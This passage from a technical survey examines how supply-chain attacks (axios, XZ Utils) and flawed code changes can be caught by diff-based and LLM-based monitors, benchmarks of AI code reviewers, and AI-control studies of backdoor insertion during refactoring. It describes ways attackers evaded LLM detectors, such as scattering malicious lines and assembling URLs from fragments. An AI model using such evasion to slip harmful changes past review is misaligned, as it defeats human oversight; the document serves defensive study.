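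Wyss and colleagues also tried to fool the models by scattering malicious lines through a large update or disguising suspicious operations, for instance by building a web address from fragments of a few letters. Either trick alone fooled GPT-4-Turbo and Gemini, but GPT-4o missed the attack only when the researchers combined them. Adding an instruction to call the update harmless never worked, because all three models treated the instruction itself as a sign of malice. Stronger models may be harder to fool, but an attacker can still hide a small change in a large diff.

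### Are diffs better than whole packages?

Wyss and colleagues compared diffs with whole packages for length and cost but measured accuracy only on smart diffs, so these results don't show that models judge diffs more accurately than whole packages. Guo and colleagues ran 11 detectors on 6,420 malicious and 7,288 harmless npm packages, but they could not include the diff-based tools they had identified because those tools weren't publicly available.

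Their results do show that judging whole packages can work well, especially with a different kind of reference. The best detector, IntelGuard, had an F1 of 96%. It retrieves information about known malware for a language model to compare with the package. The researchers also rebuilt an earlier tool, SocketAI, with the same language model. SocketAI judged the code alone, and its recall was 49 percentage points lower than IntelGuard's. Examples of known attacks can evidently help a judge as well as a clean version can, though they probably help less when an attack is new.

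Guo and colleagues also found that 21% of the malware was in places that code-analysis tools don't examine. For example, a tool that reads only JavaScript files misses a malicious command in package.json. A diff of the complete release includes package.json, where the change to axios was made.

### Datadog's monitor for pull requests

A monitor can also check changes before they reach a release. The software company Datadog uses a tool named BewAIre to review its pull requests, nearly 10,000 a week. Lamb, Hamsen and colleagues describe the tool in *Detecting malicious pull requests at scale with LLMs*. It gives a language model each diff with some context, such as the author and the type of repository. It splits diffs that are too long into chunks and flags the whole pull request if the model flags any chunk. An attack spread across several chunks could escape detection if each chunk looked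 harmless by itself.

Datadog reports these results on a set of several hundred pull requests:

- Accuracy was above 99.3%.
- Balanced accuracy, the average of recall and the share of harmless changes that the tool passes, was above 93.5%.
- The false-positive rate was 0.03%.
- The tool caught every malicious change linked to the npm attacks in Datadog's own collection.

The balanced accuracy is the most informative figure. If the tool passed nearly all harmless changes, a balanced accuracy of 93.5% implies a recall of about 87%, so the tool missed roughly one attack in eight. The overall accuracy is higher because no more than about 5% of the set can have been malicious. The recall is therefore based on a few dozen attacks at most.

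A false-positive rate of 0.03% is about one in 3,300, too low to measure on a few hundred pull requests. The figure may come from the months when Datadog ran the tool on its own code. At 10,000 pull requests a week, it would mean about three false alarms, compared with 1,000 or more at the early prototype's rate of over 10%.

Datadog produced these figures for its own product. It assembled and labelled the test set, which includes attacks that its staff and language models invented, and spent six months adjusting the tool to avoid the false alarms it had found. An outside test on unfamiliar code would probably give worse results.

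BewAIre also wouldn't have detected the axios attack if axios had used it, because the attacker published directly to npm without opening a pull request.

### Where the XZ backdoor was hidden

The axios attack was visible when the release was compared with the previous one, and it would also have been visible in a comparison with the project's public source repository. Socket's *Supply Chain Attack on Axios Pulls Malicious Dependency from npm* (2026) notes that the repository had no version tagged 1.14.1. An earlier attack, on XZ Utils, shows that a monitor's choice of reference can matter a great deal.

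XZ Utils is a set of compression tools used across Linux systems. In March 2024, Andres Freund, a software developer, noticed that remote logins on a test system were using a lot of processor time and taking about 0.8 seconds instead of 0.3. He traced the delay to a backdoor in XZ versions 5.6.0 and 5.6.1 (Freund, 2024, *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*).

The attacker had hidden most of the backdoor in compressed test files in the public repository. A small trigger was only in the release archives, the packaged source code that Linux distributions download and build. During a build, the trigger extracted the hidden code and added it to the finished program. It did this only under certain conditions, such as when the build was for a Debian or RPM package, the two main package formats for Linux.

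Comparing the release archive with the repository would have revealed the trigger but not the hidden code, a flaw shared by both. Finding the trigger would have been enough to stop the attack, because the hidden code did nothing without it. But the trigger would have been easy to miss. *Verified Reproducible Tarballs* (2025) explains that release archives normally contain many generated or copied files that are not in the repository, and that checking them all is tedious. The attacker had put the trigger in a copy of a standard build script called build-to-host. The original script was a better reference for this file than the repository, and Freund found that it did not contain the malicious line.

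Comparing version 5.6.0 of XZ Utils with the previous release would have shown both parts of the backdoor, but the hidden code would have looked like new compressed test files, which a reviewer can't easily read. Comparing version 5.6.1 with 5.6.0 would have shown only the attacker's adjustments, because 5.6.0 already contained the backdoor.

### Rebuilding a release from its source

Most people install finished programs and never see the source code. A *reproducible build* lets them check whether a program came from that source code. *Reproducibility is Not Enough* (2026) defines a build as reproducible if an independent party can use the same source code, build environment and instructions to produce a bit-for-bit identical copy. The independent copy then serves as a substitute reference for checking the published one.

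Two builds of the same source code often differ even when nobody has tampered with either. Common causes include timestamps, the names of folders on the builder's computer and the order in which the computer lists files. *No Snake Oil* (2026) examined 5,908 Python releases that Google's OSS Rebuild had successfully rebuilt, and only 1,131 of the rebuilds, or 19%, were identical to the published version. Raising an alarm for every mismatch would have flagged the other 81%.

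The rebuild may also start from the wrong source. In the same study, the source files matched for 93.8% of the releases that both OSS Rebuild and a second tool had rebuilt. In *On the Variability of Source Code in Maven Package Rebuilds*, Dietrich (2026) studied 85 releases of 28 popular Java packages that Google or Oracle had rebuilt. Differences in the source code came mainly from tools that generate code during the build.

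OSS Rebuild therefore ignores harmless differences between the published package and its own rebuilt copy, such as those caused by file compression. According to *Introducing OSS Rebuild* (Suozzo, 2025), the system works out how to build a package, rebuilds it and removes these differences from both copies before comparing them. If the copies match, it publishes a signed statement that others can check. If the published package contains code that isn't in the public repository, it gets no such statement.

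But the lack of a statement is only weak evidence of an attack. Google's *OSS Rebuild* page says that the project rebuilds only the most popular packages in each registry, and some legitimate packages are hard to rebuild. A package that had always matched its rebuild and then stopped matching would be more suspicious.

Rebuilding a release doesn't reveal tampering if both builders start from the same tampered source. In a 2026 talk, Suozzo said that the backdoored XZ package was fully reproducible because the release archive used for the rebuild already contained the trigger. *How NixOS could have detected the XZ supply-chain attack* (2025) proposes obtaining the source independently, rebuilding from it and checking whether the results are identical. A build from the repository would have lacked the trigger, so its output would have differed from the backdoored program. *Reproducible Builds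 and Insights from an Independent Verifier for Arch Linux* (2025) points out that even independent sources don't help if every builder uses the same compromised compiler.

The two attacks would have looked different against each reference:

| Reference | Axios 1.14.1 | XZ Utils 5.6.0 |
|---|---|---|
| Previous release | One added dependency | Trigger and new test files, among other changes |
| Public repository | No matching version | Trigger, among many generated files |
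| Rebuild from the published source archive | No difference | No difference under the same build conditions |
| Rebuild from the repository | No matching source to build | A program without the backdoor |

After the XZ attack, Google's team started to record what happens during a build as well as its result. The record covers which programs run, which files they read and write, and what they download. The team can then compare it with the record of the previous version's build. In the XZ case, the build went from reading no test files to reading three, although the tests were switched off. A simple tool for copying part of a file also wrote a piece of compiled code, which normally only a compiler does.

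Suozzo acknowledges that these signs are easier to spot in hindsight. But two successive versions of a package usually build in much the same way, so there may be few differences to check. Legitimate projects can still add noise, for example by running tests during the build. Programs that run inside Python or Java are also harder to record in detail.

### First releases and new dependencies

A package's first release has no earlier release to compare it with. Attackers can exploit this by publishing a new package with a name that people may mistake for that of a popular package, or by adding a new malicious package to one that people already trust.

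The axios attacker gave plain-crypto-js a history by publishing a harmless version, 4.2.0, on the morning of 30 March, then released the malicious 4.2.1 just before midnight UTC. Comparing the two versions would have exposed the new installation script. But Elastic's monitor covered only the 15,000 most downloaded packages, and a package less than a day old was very unlikely to be among them.

Socket's scanner flagged version 4.2.1 of the dependency within six minutes, about 15 minutes before the attacker published the first malicious version of axios. The scanner examined the dependency itself, which contained the malware, while comparing axios versions could reveal only that someone had added the dependency.

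For some first releases, the monitor can use another package as the reference. Version 4.2.1 was a copy of the real crypto-js with malware added, and Datadog Security Labs' comparison of the two shows the added installation script. Wyss and colleagues similarly compared 163 malicious copies with the originals. This works only if the new package copies an existing one and the monitor can find the original.

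Another option is to compare new software with a baseline profile. Guo and colleagues describe EMPHunter, a detector that groups the installation scripts of new packages by similarity and ranks the unusual ones for review. Only about 2.2% of npm packages have scripts that run on installation, so having one is a reason to look more closely at a package. But many of these scripts are harmless, and malware can also be elsewhere in a package.

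Without a reference, the monitor has to judge the whole package on its own. This is difficult because honest and malicious packages use many of the same operations, so the monitor has to work out what the code is for. For example, the command that starts a package's build can also give an attacker remote control.

A monitor that compares releases should therefore fetch every newly added dependency and judge it in full, along with anything that dependency installs. This would have taken little work for axios, because the malicious installer was only 4,209 bytes long. Its text was scrambled, but that was itself suspicious, and the scrambling couldn't hide what the installer did when it ran. StepSecurity reports that the malware contacted the attacker's server within two seconds of an installation starting, and that a tool watching the network connections of build machines detected it.

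## Reviewing code changes for security flaws

The axios attacker added code that had no legitimate purpose, but most security flaws enter software when a developer gets a detail wrong in a useful change and a reviewer approves it. Anyone, including an AI agent, could disguise a deliberate flaw as this kind of mistake.

*Can Agentic Code Review Catch Vulnerabilities Before They Are Merged?* (Yang, Yang and colleagues, 2026) tested whether AI agents notice such flaws. Its benchmark, SecPRBench, contains 265 real changes to nine widely used systems, including the browser Firefox, Chrome's JavaScript engine V8 and the encryption library OpenSSL. Nearly all the changes introduced a vulnerability, and seven were failed attempts to remove one. Each comes with a second version that includes the later repair.

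Earlier benchmarks mostly created a flawed change by undoing all or part of a repair, so the diff centred on the flawed code. In SecPRBench, the agents saw the original change with all its unrelated edits. The median change touched four files and 173 lines.

Each agent received the diff, the developer's message describing the change, and a searchable copy of the whole repository. It did not receive the version history or any information about the flaw. Unlike the models in the Lucene experiment, it received no label for the old version. A developer's description of a change can bias a reviewer.

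### One test input, three versions

Public records of a vulnerability usually identify the change that repaired it but not the one that introduced it. The researchers had an AI agent trace the affected code back from the repair to a likely source. Such tracing is often wrong, so they checked most of the results by building and running three versions of the software:

1. the version just before the suspected change
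2. the version with the change
3. the version with both the change and the later repair

They ran all three versions on the same input, one that triggers the flaw, such as a malformed file. They confirmed the case only if the failure occurred in the second version but not in the first or third.

This check is a differential test, but it compares the software's behavior rather than its text. If the version from before the change also fails, the flaw was probably already there. If the repaired version still fails, either the repair is incomplete or the input triggers a different problem. Crashes with another cause did not count. Automatic checks, mainly this one, confirmed 217 cases, and people decided the other 48.

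Some of those 48 show what running the software can miss. In one Firefox case, one part of the program could write text while another part was reading it. The test ran without a memory error, and only the source code showed that nothing coordinated the two. In a case from FreeType, a library for drawing fonts, the program used a point outside the valid range, but it had reserved more memory than it needed, so the error detector found nothing.

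The seven failed repairs left flaws that both versions shared. In one, an SQLite developer tried to stop the program from reading past the end of a damaged zip file, but the new check used a header length of 30 bytes instead of the 46 it needed. The same input triggered the flaw in both versions, so comparing their behaviour would have shown no difference, but the diff contained the faulty check.

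A monitor can test a new change this way only if it has an input that triggers the flaw. Yang and colleagues could reuse inputs from public reports or generate new ones from what was already known about each flaw.

### How many flaws the agents found

An agent got credit only if it explained what triggers the flaw, which operation becomes unsafe and which safeguard is missing or wrong. Claude Opus 5.5, which was also one of the models being tested, judged the explanations against a reference description. Using Claude Sonnet 4.6 as the judge instead would have changed the verdict on only seven of Opus 5.5's 265 reviews, some in each direction. The two judges agreed on 96.9% of the reports that contained any findings.

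| Model | Recall | Misses with a finding in the right file | Findings per flawed change | Findings per repaired change |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Grok 4.6 | 78.1% | 79.3% | 3.1 | 3.0 |
| GPT-6 sol | 76.2% | 61.9% | 3.1 | 2.7 |
| GLM 5.3 | 74.7% | 92.5% | 3.6 | 3.4 |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | 74.0% | 84.1% | 2.6 | 2.2 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 59.2% | 75.9% | 2.2 | 2.1 |
| GPT-5.6 sol | 55.8% | 53.8% | 1.7 | 1.2 |
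| GPT-6 luna | 55.5% | 55.9% | 1.6 | 1.2 |
| MiniMax M3 | 32.5% | 61.5% | 2.2 | 2.4 |

*Results on the 265 changes. The "right file" is any file that a reader needs in order to understand the flaw's cause.*

The differences among the top four models are not statistically significant. On harder flaws, which only one to three of the other models found, each of the top four found about half, while the rest found between 5% and 19%. Errors in a program's logic were harder to find than unsafe uses of memory, with average recall of 51.5% compared with 73.1%.

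All eight models missed the same 23 flaws. If their errors were independent, the expected number of flaws missed by all eight would be less than one. Grok, GPT-6 sol and GLM together found 238 flaws, and adding the other five models raised the total only to 242. A monitor therefore gains much less from extra models than one would expect from each model's recall. The 23 flaws may be very hard to find, but shared training data, overly strict grading criteria or errors by the judge could also explain why no model was credited with finding them.

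### The right file, the wrong explanation

In 68% of the misses, the agent reported a problem in the right file but gave the wrong explanation. Finding the file was easy, because the diff nearly always included it. The agent opened the right file and reported nothing in only about 22% of misses.

A nine-line change to curl, a program for transferring data, shows why the explanation matters. After the change, the program kept a pointer into a block of memory that it would later release. Using the pointer after the release is dangerous because the memory may hold something else by then. All eight agents reported a problem in the file, but four described a memory leak, which is a failure to release memory the program no longer needs. A developer who acted on that report would look for memory to release, which wouldn't fix the pointer.

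*From Verdict to Diagnosis* (Chen, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes a pull request that let users supply the identifier of a saved run. A function that the pull request left unchanged looked up the run without checking that it belonged to the user's current project, so users could reach other projects' data. An AI reviewer blocked the change, but over an unrelated concern about secrets appearing in the user's browser. A monitor that records only whether the reviewer objected would count this review as a success, even though fixing the problem the reviewer raised would have left other projects' data exposed.

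To measure how often this happens, Chen and colleagues compared their own reviewer, PRGuard, with CodeRabbit, a widely used commercial reviewer. On 31 harmful pull requests, the two blocked nearly the same number, but PRGuard identified 1.38 times as many of the flaws. In 14 harmful changes, the flaw was a missing safeguard, such as a check of who owns the data. Both tools blocked nine of these, and PRGuard identified three times as many of the flaws. Because the researchers designed both PRGuard and the test, the size of its advantage is less certain than the finding that a tool can block a harmful change without identifying its flaw.

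To explain some flaws, a reviewer must connect code in several files. In SecPRBench, average recall was 69.6% for flaws whose cause was in one file and 38.5% for those whose cause spread over five or more. Large changes are harder to review anyway, but a gap remained among diffs that touched at least six files, where recall was 59.0% for causes in one file and 38.6% for causes in five or more. The comparison doesn't prove that the spread itself made the flaws harder to find, because the flaws also differed in other ways. Outside V8, the project where the agents did worst, recall fell only from 70.3% to 51.6%, and the second figure is based on eight flaws.

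### A flaw outside the diff

One of the changes was to Wasmtime, which runs programs in a compact format called WebAssembly and isolates them from the host computer. A WebAssembly program can use *tables*, which are lists of references to functions and other objects. It can define its own tables and import others. Wasmtime has two ways to number them: one counts every table, starting with the imported ones, and the other counts only the tables that the program defines. For a program that imports one table and defines two, the numbers would be:

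| Table | Number among all tables | Number among the program's own tables |
|---|---|---|
| Imported table | 0 | None |
| First table of its own | 1 | 0 |
| Second table of its own | 2 | 1 |

The change affected the function that carries out the `table.fill` instruction, which writes a value into a range of table entries. After the change, the function expected a number from the last column. But Winch, one of Wasmtime's compilers, still produced calls that passed a number from the middle column.

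If the program tried to fill its first table, Winch would pass 1 and the function would fill the second table instead. If it tried to fill its second table, Winch would pass 2. No table has that number in the last column, so Wasmtime would crash.

*CVE-2026-34946 Detail*, an entry in the US government's National Vulnerability Database (NVD), attributes the flaw to a code reorganisation that left Winch out. The flaw let a program crash the host or modify the wrong table, but do nothing worse, and the entry lists it as medium severity.

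The Winch code was not in the diff because nobody had edited it. It looked reasonable by itself, and it had matched the function until the change. To explain the flaw, a reviewer had to notice in the diff that the function now expected a different number, then find the code that called it and check which number that code passed. Someone reading the whole new version without a diff could also have found the mismatch, but would have had no particular reason to check this function first.

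Yang and colleagues required agents to make this connection. Agents got no credit for a general warning that the table number might be out of range, even if they pointed to the right call.

### What the agents reported after the repair

The agents also reviewed each change with the later repair included. The judge never credited any agent with finding the original flaw in a repaired version. This follows from how the judge awarded credit, so it does not show that the false-positive rate was zero.

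The judge credited a finding only if it described the original flaw and the flaw was still in the code. Once a repair had removed the flaw, the judge would therefore have recorded no detection even if an agent had repeated its earlier warning word for word. To count such false alarms, the judge would have to ignore whether the flaw was still there and decide only whether the agent had described it.

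The agents' other findings on the repaired versions don't provide a false-positive rate either, because some of them may describe real problems. The researchers checked that the repair removed one particular flaw, but not that the rest of the change was clean. The agents also searched a later copy of the repository that could include other developers' changes.

Agents keep reporting problems in the repaired versions, after the main one is gone. Grok's average number of findings fell only from 3.1 to 3.0, and GLM reported something on 97.4% of the repaired changes. Across all eight models, 74.9% of reviews of repaired changes included a finding in a file connected with the original flaw. For flawed changes, the share was about 88%, assuming that every correct explanation also pointed to such a file. A monitor that raised an alarm whenever an agent mentioned one of these files would therefore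 barely distinguish flawed changes from repaired ones.

The agents responded to some repairs. When an agent's only finding on the flawed version was correct, it reported nothing on the repaired version 44% of the time, compared with 16% when its only finding was wrong. One would expect this difference if agents that had understood the flaw were more likely to notice that it was gone.

Without a false-positive rate, it is also hard to tell whether higher recall makes a better monitor. The researchers ran Claude Opus 5.5 in Anthropic's Defending Code, a set of tools and instructions for security review. On the 260 changes it finished reviewing, recall rose from 73.8% to 81.5%, but the average number of findings rose from 2.5 to 8.4 and the median cost from $0.35 to $3.65. With OpenAI's Codex Security, GPT-5.6 sol's recall fell from 55.8% to 47.5% and its average number of findings from 1.7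 to 1.2, mostly because the agent more often reported nothing.

Chen and colleagues designed their benchmark to count some false positives. It includes 50 harmless pull requests, each containing the complete repair for a matching harmful one. Because the reviewer must decide whether to block each change, blocking a harmless one can be counted as a false positive. However, the surrounding code may still contain unrelated flaws, so an occasional block might be justified.

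### How much context a reviewer needs

Every agent in SecPRBench received both the diff and the repository, so the study does not test whether judging a diff works better than judging the whole code. A direct test would give some agents only the diff, others only the new version and a third group both. Several other studies come closer to this test by varying how much surrounding code a model receives.

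Kumar's experiments are the strongest reason to be cautious about adding context. Eight models did worse when given more than the diff and a summary. Claude Sonnet 4.6's score for problems that depend on unchanged code in the same file fell from 0.22 to 0.10 when Kumar added information about that code. The two Mistral models, unlike the other six, recovered slightly when Kumar also added information about the tests. However, the models could not look anything up for themselves, and only one of the 350 pull requests in the collection was a security fix.

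*AACR-Bench* found much smaller effects. It covers 200 pull requests in ten programming languages and 1,505 problems that engineers had confirmed. Half of the problems were visible in the diff, about a third required the rest of the file, and the others required information from elsewhere in the project. Every model received the diff and the pull request's title and description. In two of the four tests, it also received three pieces of code, found either by matching keywords or by comparing meaning. In the last test, the model worked as an agent in Claude Code and looked up code itself.

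| Model | No added code | Keyword search | Search by meaning | Agent |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude 4.5 Sonnet | 0.145 | 0.146 | 0.135 | 0.161 |
| GPT-5.2 | 0.122 | 0.117 | 0.117 | 0.046 |
| GLM-4.7 | 0.160 | 0.156 | 0.156 | 0.067 |
| DeepSeek-V3.2 | 0.097 | 0.100 | 0.089 | 0.067 |
| Qwen3-Coder-480B | 0.140 | 0.147 | 0.144 | 0.068 |

*F1 by method. The keyword-search scores are matched to models using the recall figures that the paper gives for each type of problem.*

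According to the paper, keyword search reduced Claude's F1 by 31%, but the main results appear to list the keyword-search scores under the wrong model names. With the names corrected, neither kind of search changed any model's F1 by 0.01 or more.

Working as an agent made a much larger difference. Claude's precision rose from 8.7% to 39.9%, but its recall fell from 42.9% to 10.1% because it made far fewer comments. The other four models also made fewer comments, but their precision did not rise comparably, and their F1 fell. Claude Code, Anthropic's own product, may have suited Claude better than the other models.

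Even without extra code, GPT-5.2 found 43% of the problems that supposedly required information from elsewhere in the project, compared with 51% of those visible in the diff. This may be partly because the first group includes problems that depend on the pull request's title or description, which every model saw. Most of the 1,505 problems came from reviews written by AI models and checked by engineers, so the collection probably favours problems that models can find.

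*Improving LLM-Based Go Code Review through Issue-List Generation and Context Augmentation* (Sun, Guan and colleagues, 2026) reports more encouraging results for carefully chosen context in reviews of code written in the programming language Go. DeepSeek-V3 reviewed 1,438 short code changes and listed possible problems in each. A second model then revised the code in response to each comment. A review counted as successful if at least one of these revisions exactly matched the developers' final version.

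| Code added to the diff | Average lines added | Comments per change | Success rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 0 | 3.1 | 21.8% |
| Random code from files in the same commit | 149 | 3.9 | 23.0% |
| The function containing the change | 67 | 3.7 | 23.6% |
| Definitions and uses of the names in the changed lines | 81 | 3.7 | 23.7% |
| Similar code from files in the same commit | 83 | 3.9 | 24.0% |
| The function and similar code | 149 | 4.1 | 25.6% |
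| All three chosen types | 216 | 4.3 | 24.9% |

Adding random code produced about a third of the best improvement, perhaps partly because the model made more comments and so had more chances to succeed. But the choice of code also seems to matter, because adding the function containing the change helped more than random code did, even though the function was less than half as long and led to fewer comments. Adding the third type reduced the success rate slightly, and the researchers give examples in which the extra code apparently distracted the model from a problem it had otherwise found.

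Combining the comments from reviews with no added code and reviews with the best pair of additions raised the success rate to 28.0%, so each kind of review found some problems that the other missed. However, the combined list averaged 7.2 comments per change. Even comments by human reviewers led to the right revision only 36.1% of the time, which suggests that the second model was responsible for many of the failures. The study covered code review in general, so added context may help more in finding security flaws that depend on distant code.

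Yildiz, Teo and colleagues (2025), in *Benchmarking LLMs and LLM-based Agents in Practical Vulnerability Detection for Code Repositories*, did study security flaws, but they showed models whole functions without a diff. Their benchmark, JitVul, has 879 pairs, each consisting of a vulnerable function and its repaired version. The model judged each version separately, and a pair counted as correct only if it got both right. GPT-4o's results were:

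| What GPT-4o could see | Basic prompt | Asked to reason step by step |
|---|---|---|
| The function alone | 1.0% | 15.0% |
| The function and up to five related functions | 1.0% | 18.7% |
| The function, with tools to look up others | 17.6% | 19.1% |

*Share of pairs in which GPT-4o judged both versions correctly.*

Asking the model to reason step by step, without showing it any extra code, produced most of the large gain that looking up other functions seemed to give with the basic prompt. None of these results is good, since random guessing would get 25% of pairs right. The most common error was to call both versions vulnerable. GPT-4o dates from 2024, and the models in SecPRBench are much more capable, so the low scores are weak evidence about current agents. The comparison still shows that an agent may do better because it reasons more rather than because it sees more code.

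Security instructions can have a similar effect. *AgenticSCR* (Charoenwet, Tantithamthavorn and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that reviews a code change before the developer saves it to the project's history, starting from the diff and exploring the repository. Of the agent's comments, 17.5% identified the right lines, described the problem and named the right type of flaw, compared with about 7% for a model with a fixed prompt. But the agent also had a set of security rules and a second agent to check its findings. The full system made 81% fewer comments than a basic agent without this security knowledge, and the share that were relevant and in the right place was 10.2 percentage points higher. Much of its advantage may therefore have come from the security knowledge it was given.

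## Agent-written changes compared with the request and the original behaviour

A security review usually doesn't question the purpose of a change. When an AI agent has written the change, a monitor must also check that the agent did what the user asked. Comparing the new code with the old version isn't enough, because a requested change should also make the code different. A requested feature can look much like a backdoor in a diff, since both appear as added lines.

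The monitor therefore needs another way to determine which differences to expect. For most changes, it can use the user's request as a substitute reference. For *refactoring*, which means reorganising code without altering what it does, the reference can be the original program, whose behaviour the new version should match.

### How ARCTIC compares a change with the request

Meta built a system called ARCTIC to help its engineers review code written by AI agents. Maddila, Rashik and colleagues (2026), in *From Code Review to Code Critique*, explain how it measures "drift", the gap between what the developer wanted and what the agent did:

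1. A language model infers the developer's intent from the conversation with the agent, the agent's plan, the title and summary of the change, and linked documents. It doesn't see the code change, because it might then describe the code and call that the intent.
2. A model reads the diff and turns it into a numbered list of what changed, without seeing the conversation or the summary. The researchers call this step "backtranslation".
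3. A model compares the list with the intent and gives a drift score from 0 to 100. The scale has five bands, from "perfect alignment" to "major drift".

Suppose a developer asks an agent to stop an app from hanging when an outside service doesn't respond. The list of changes might show that the agent added a five-second timeout and turned off the check of the service's security certificate. The timeout serves the developer's intent, but nothing in the request explains why the agent turned off the certificate check.

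ARCTIC distinguishes two kinds of drift: failures to follow instructions and unrequested changes. If the agent had put the timeout on the wrong call, it would have failed to follow instructions, which always raises the score. Turning off the certificate check is an unrequested change, which raises the score only if it is risky or clearly out of scope. Adding a useful safety check that nobody requested doesn't raise the score. The model therefore has to judge whether each extra change is harmful, in addition to making the comparison.

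Even when the code is hidden in the first step, the agent can still influence the inferred intent, because the conversation includes its replies and it may also have written the plan and the summary. If the agent wrote that it would "relax" the certificate check and the developer didn't object, the model might treat this as part of the intent. That is reasonable for catching misunderstandings, since developers often accept an agent's suggestions. A monitor for deliberate harm would do better to rely on the developer's own messages and on documents the agent can't edit. Even then, it would miss harm that the developer requested.

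### How closely ARCTIC agrees with people

Maddila and colleagues tested the drift scores on 118 diffs that people had also scored. They chose the diffs so that each band had between 18 and 31. The model picked the same band as the human raters for 76 diffs, or 64.4%, but its "quadratic weighted kappa" was 0.907. This measure of agreement depends on how far apart the two ratings are:

kappa = 1 − (average squared distance between the ratings) / (average squared distance if the ratings were paired at random)

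A value of 1 means perfect agreement, and 0 means agreement no better than chance. Because the measure squares the distances, an error of two bands counts four times as much as an error of one. Here the average squared distance was about 0.4, compared with about 4.4 for random pairing. The published figures imply that about 40 of the model's 42 errors were off by a single band.

| Human rating | Diffs | Model gave the same rating | Model's ratings in this band that were right |
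|---|---|---|---|
| Perfect alignment | 24 | 83% | 95% |
| Minor drift | 18 | 78% | 58% |
| Moderate drift | 20 | 35% | 33% |
| Significant drift | 25 | 36% | 47% |
| Major drift | 31 | 84% | 79% |

An error of one band matters little to a developer who wants a rough idea of how well a change fits the request, but more to a monitor that raises an alarm above a threshold. A natural threshold would be between moderate and significant drift, where the model was least accurate. Major drift is also probably rarer in everyday work than in this balanced set, so fewer than 79% of the "major drift" ratings would be right.

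### Did seeing the score improve the code?

In spring 2026, Meta showed drift scores to engineers who used a new review interface. The researchers sampled 247 pairs of consecutive versions of a change and kept the 193 in which the earlier version scored above 25 and the intent stayed much the same. The author had used the new interface in 94 of these pairs.

Drift fell by 11.82 points on average across all 193 pairs. It fell by about 14.8 points when authors saw the score and about 9.0 when they did not, a difference of 5.76 points.

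This design gives only weak support for the claim that showing the score caused the extra reduction. Authors chose whether to use the new interface, and Maddila and colleagues acknowledge that those who did may have been more engaged or had easier changes to fix. The statistical evidence is also borderline. The reported p-value of 0.026 comes from a one-sided test for an effect in the expected direction. A two-sided test would give about 0.05, and the 95% confidence interval runs from roughly zero to 11.5 points. A rank-based test gave a p-value of 0.063.

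The selection of pairs probably explains part of the overall fall. The scores are noisy, with an average error of about 10 points, so some versions scored above 25 by chance and would have scored lower if scored again without any edits. This would bias the 5.76-point difference only if the two groups started from different levels.

The outcome measure was also the score that users saw, so they may have learned to lower it without improving the code, for example by rewording the summary from which ARCTIC infers the intent. The requirement that the intent stay similar limits this but doesn't rule it out. Showing the score to a random half of the interface's users, and having people judge the resulting code, would be a much better test.

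Meta also let authors submit some changes without a colleague reviewing them first if ARCTIC found little drift and no risky code. Meta attributed no defects to these changes, but engineers later reversed 0.33% of them, compared with 0.17% of standard changes. Both rates are low, and the two groups may have differed in other ways, but the comparison doesn't suggest that the new process was safer.

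### Most unrequested changes are not attacks

Goel, Steenhoek and Hu (2026), in *How Much Do Coding Agents Over-Edit, and Why?*, looked for unnecessary changes without inferring anyone's intent. They took 18 models' 7,660 successful solutions to coding tasks, undid one block of changed lines at a time and reran the task's tests. If the tests still passed, they counted the block as unneeded.

On SWE-bench Verified, a set of 500 Python tasks from real projects, an average of 11% of the code blocks in each agent-written solution were unneeded. The researchers ran most of these blocks, and 89% of those they ran changed what the program did. Human developers' solutions to the same tasks had slightly more unneeded code, about 14%. A monitor that raised an alarm for every unneeded change would therefore flag a lot of honest work.

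Tests miss things, so passing them doesn't prove that nobody wanted the change. A second, stricter check counted a block as needed if it changed behaviour in the same way as the developers' solution. By that measure, agents left more unneeded code than developers did, but the check favours developers almost by definition.

The size of a change is a poor warning sign too. The median model changed 2.33 times as many lines as the developers did, but 61% of the extra edits were tests and 13% were documentation.

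Asking models to check their own work helped only a little. When Goel and colleagues told models to justify each part of their solution and remove what they couldn't justify, the models removed 35.5% of the unneeded code, but about a third of what they removed was needed.

A monitor can narrow the search by asking why each extra change is there. *Probing agent overeagerness in realistic settings with continuation audits* (2026) uses a rubric that separates the core of the request from "necessary collateral" and from expansions of scope. An example of necessary collateral is editing every file that calls a renamed function, even if the user never mentioned those files. The rubric also covers whether the agent told the user about an expansion. It excuses expansions that have the user's explicit approval, which is much better evidence of intent than a failure to object.

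### Refactored code that behaved differently

Refactoring seems to offer a simpler test, since any change in behaviour is unexpected. *Improved Monitoring of Backdoor Insertion During Code Refactoring* (Lohrbeer, 2025) describes a pilot study of 60 samples based on this idea. An "honest" model received a program and its tests and reorganised the code. The result had to pass the original tests and actually refactor the program rather than copy it.

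An "attacking" model did the same but also inserted a backdoor. To prove the backdoor was there, it wrote a secret test that gave different results on the old and new programs. Lohrbeer counted any difference in behaviour as a backdoor, a definition taken from earlier research on AI control, which studies how to use AI models safely even if they try to cause harm.

An AI judge had rated some of the honest code as very suspicious, so Lohrbeer had a model try to write secret tests for the honest code as well. The model succeeded for 41% of the samples, although all the samples had passed the original tests. With only 60 samples, the true rate could plausibly be between about 29% and 53%.

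These programs met the study's definition of a backdoor, but that doesn't mean anyone could have used them to cause harm. Lohrbeer concluded that the definition should require a vulnerability, not just a difference in behaviour. A monitor using the original definition would raise about 410 false alarms for every 1,000 honest refactorings.

*A Differential Fuzzing-Based Evaluation of Functional Equivalence in LLM-Generated Code Refactorings* (Dristi and Dwyer, 2026) found fewer differences in a larger study. Six models refactored Python programs, and Dristi and Dwyer ran the old and new versions on 1,000 or 2,000 automatically generated inputs. Of 3,538 refactorings, 26% gave a different output on at least one input. The existing tests caught most of these. Assuming every equivalent refactoring passed the tests, about 7% of the refactorings that passed still behaved differently.

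How often a refactoring is found to change behaviour depends on which inputs count and how hard someone looks for a difference, which may partly explain the gap between 7% and 41%. Dristi and Dwyer generated only inputs that followed each program's rules, such as the expected types, while Lohrbeer's model deliberately searched for a difference. Lohrbeer also used longer programs, of up to 400 lines.

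### A harmless change in an edge case

Consider a Python function that checks whether a day is at the weekend:

```
def is_weekend(day):
    if day == "Saturday" or day == "Sunday":
        return True
    return False
```

An agent asked to simplify it might write:

```
def is_weekend(day):
    return day in {"Saturday", "Sunday"}
```

Both versions give the same answer for any text, so ordinary tests would pass. But if a secret test calls the function with a list, `["Saturday"]`, the old version compares the list with each word, finds no match and returns `False`. The new version tries to look the list up in a set, which Python doesn't allow, so it stops with an error. Because of this difference, the new version meets the pilot's definition of a backdoor.

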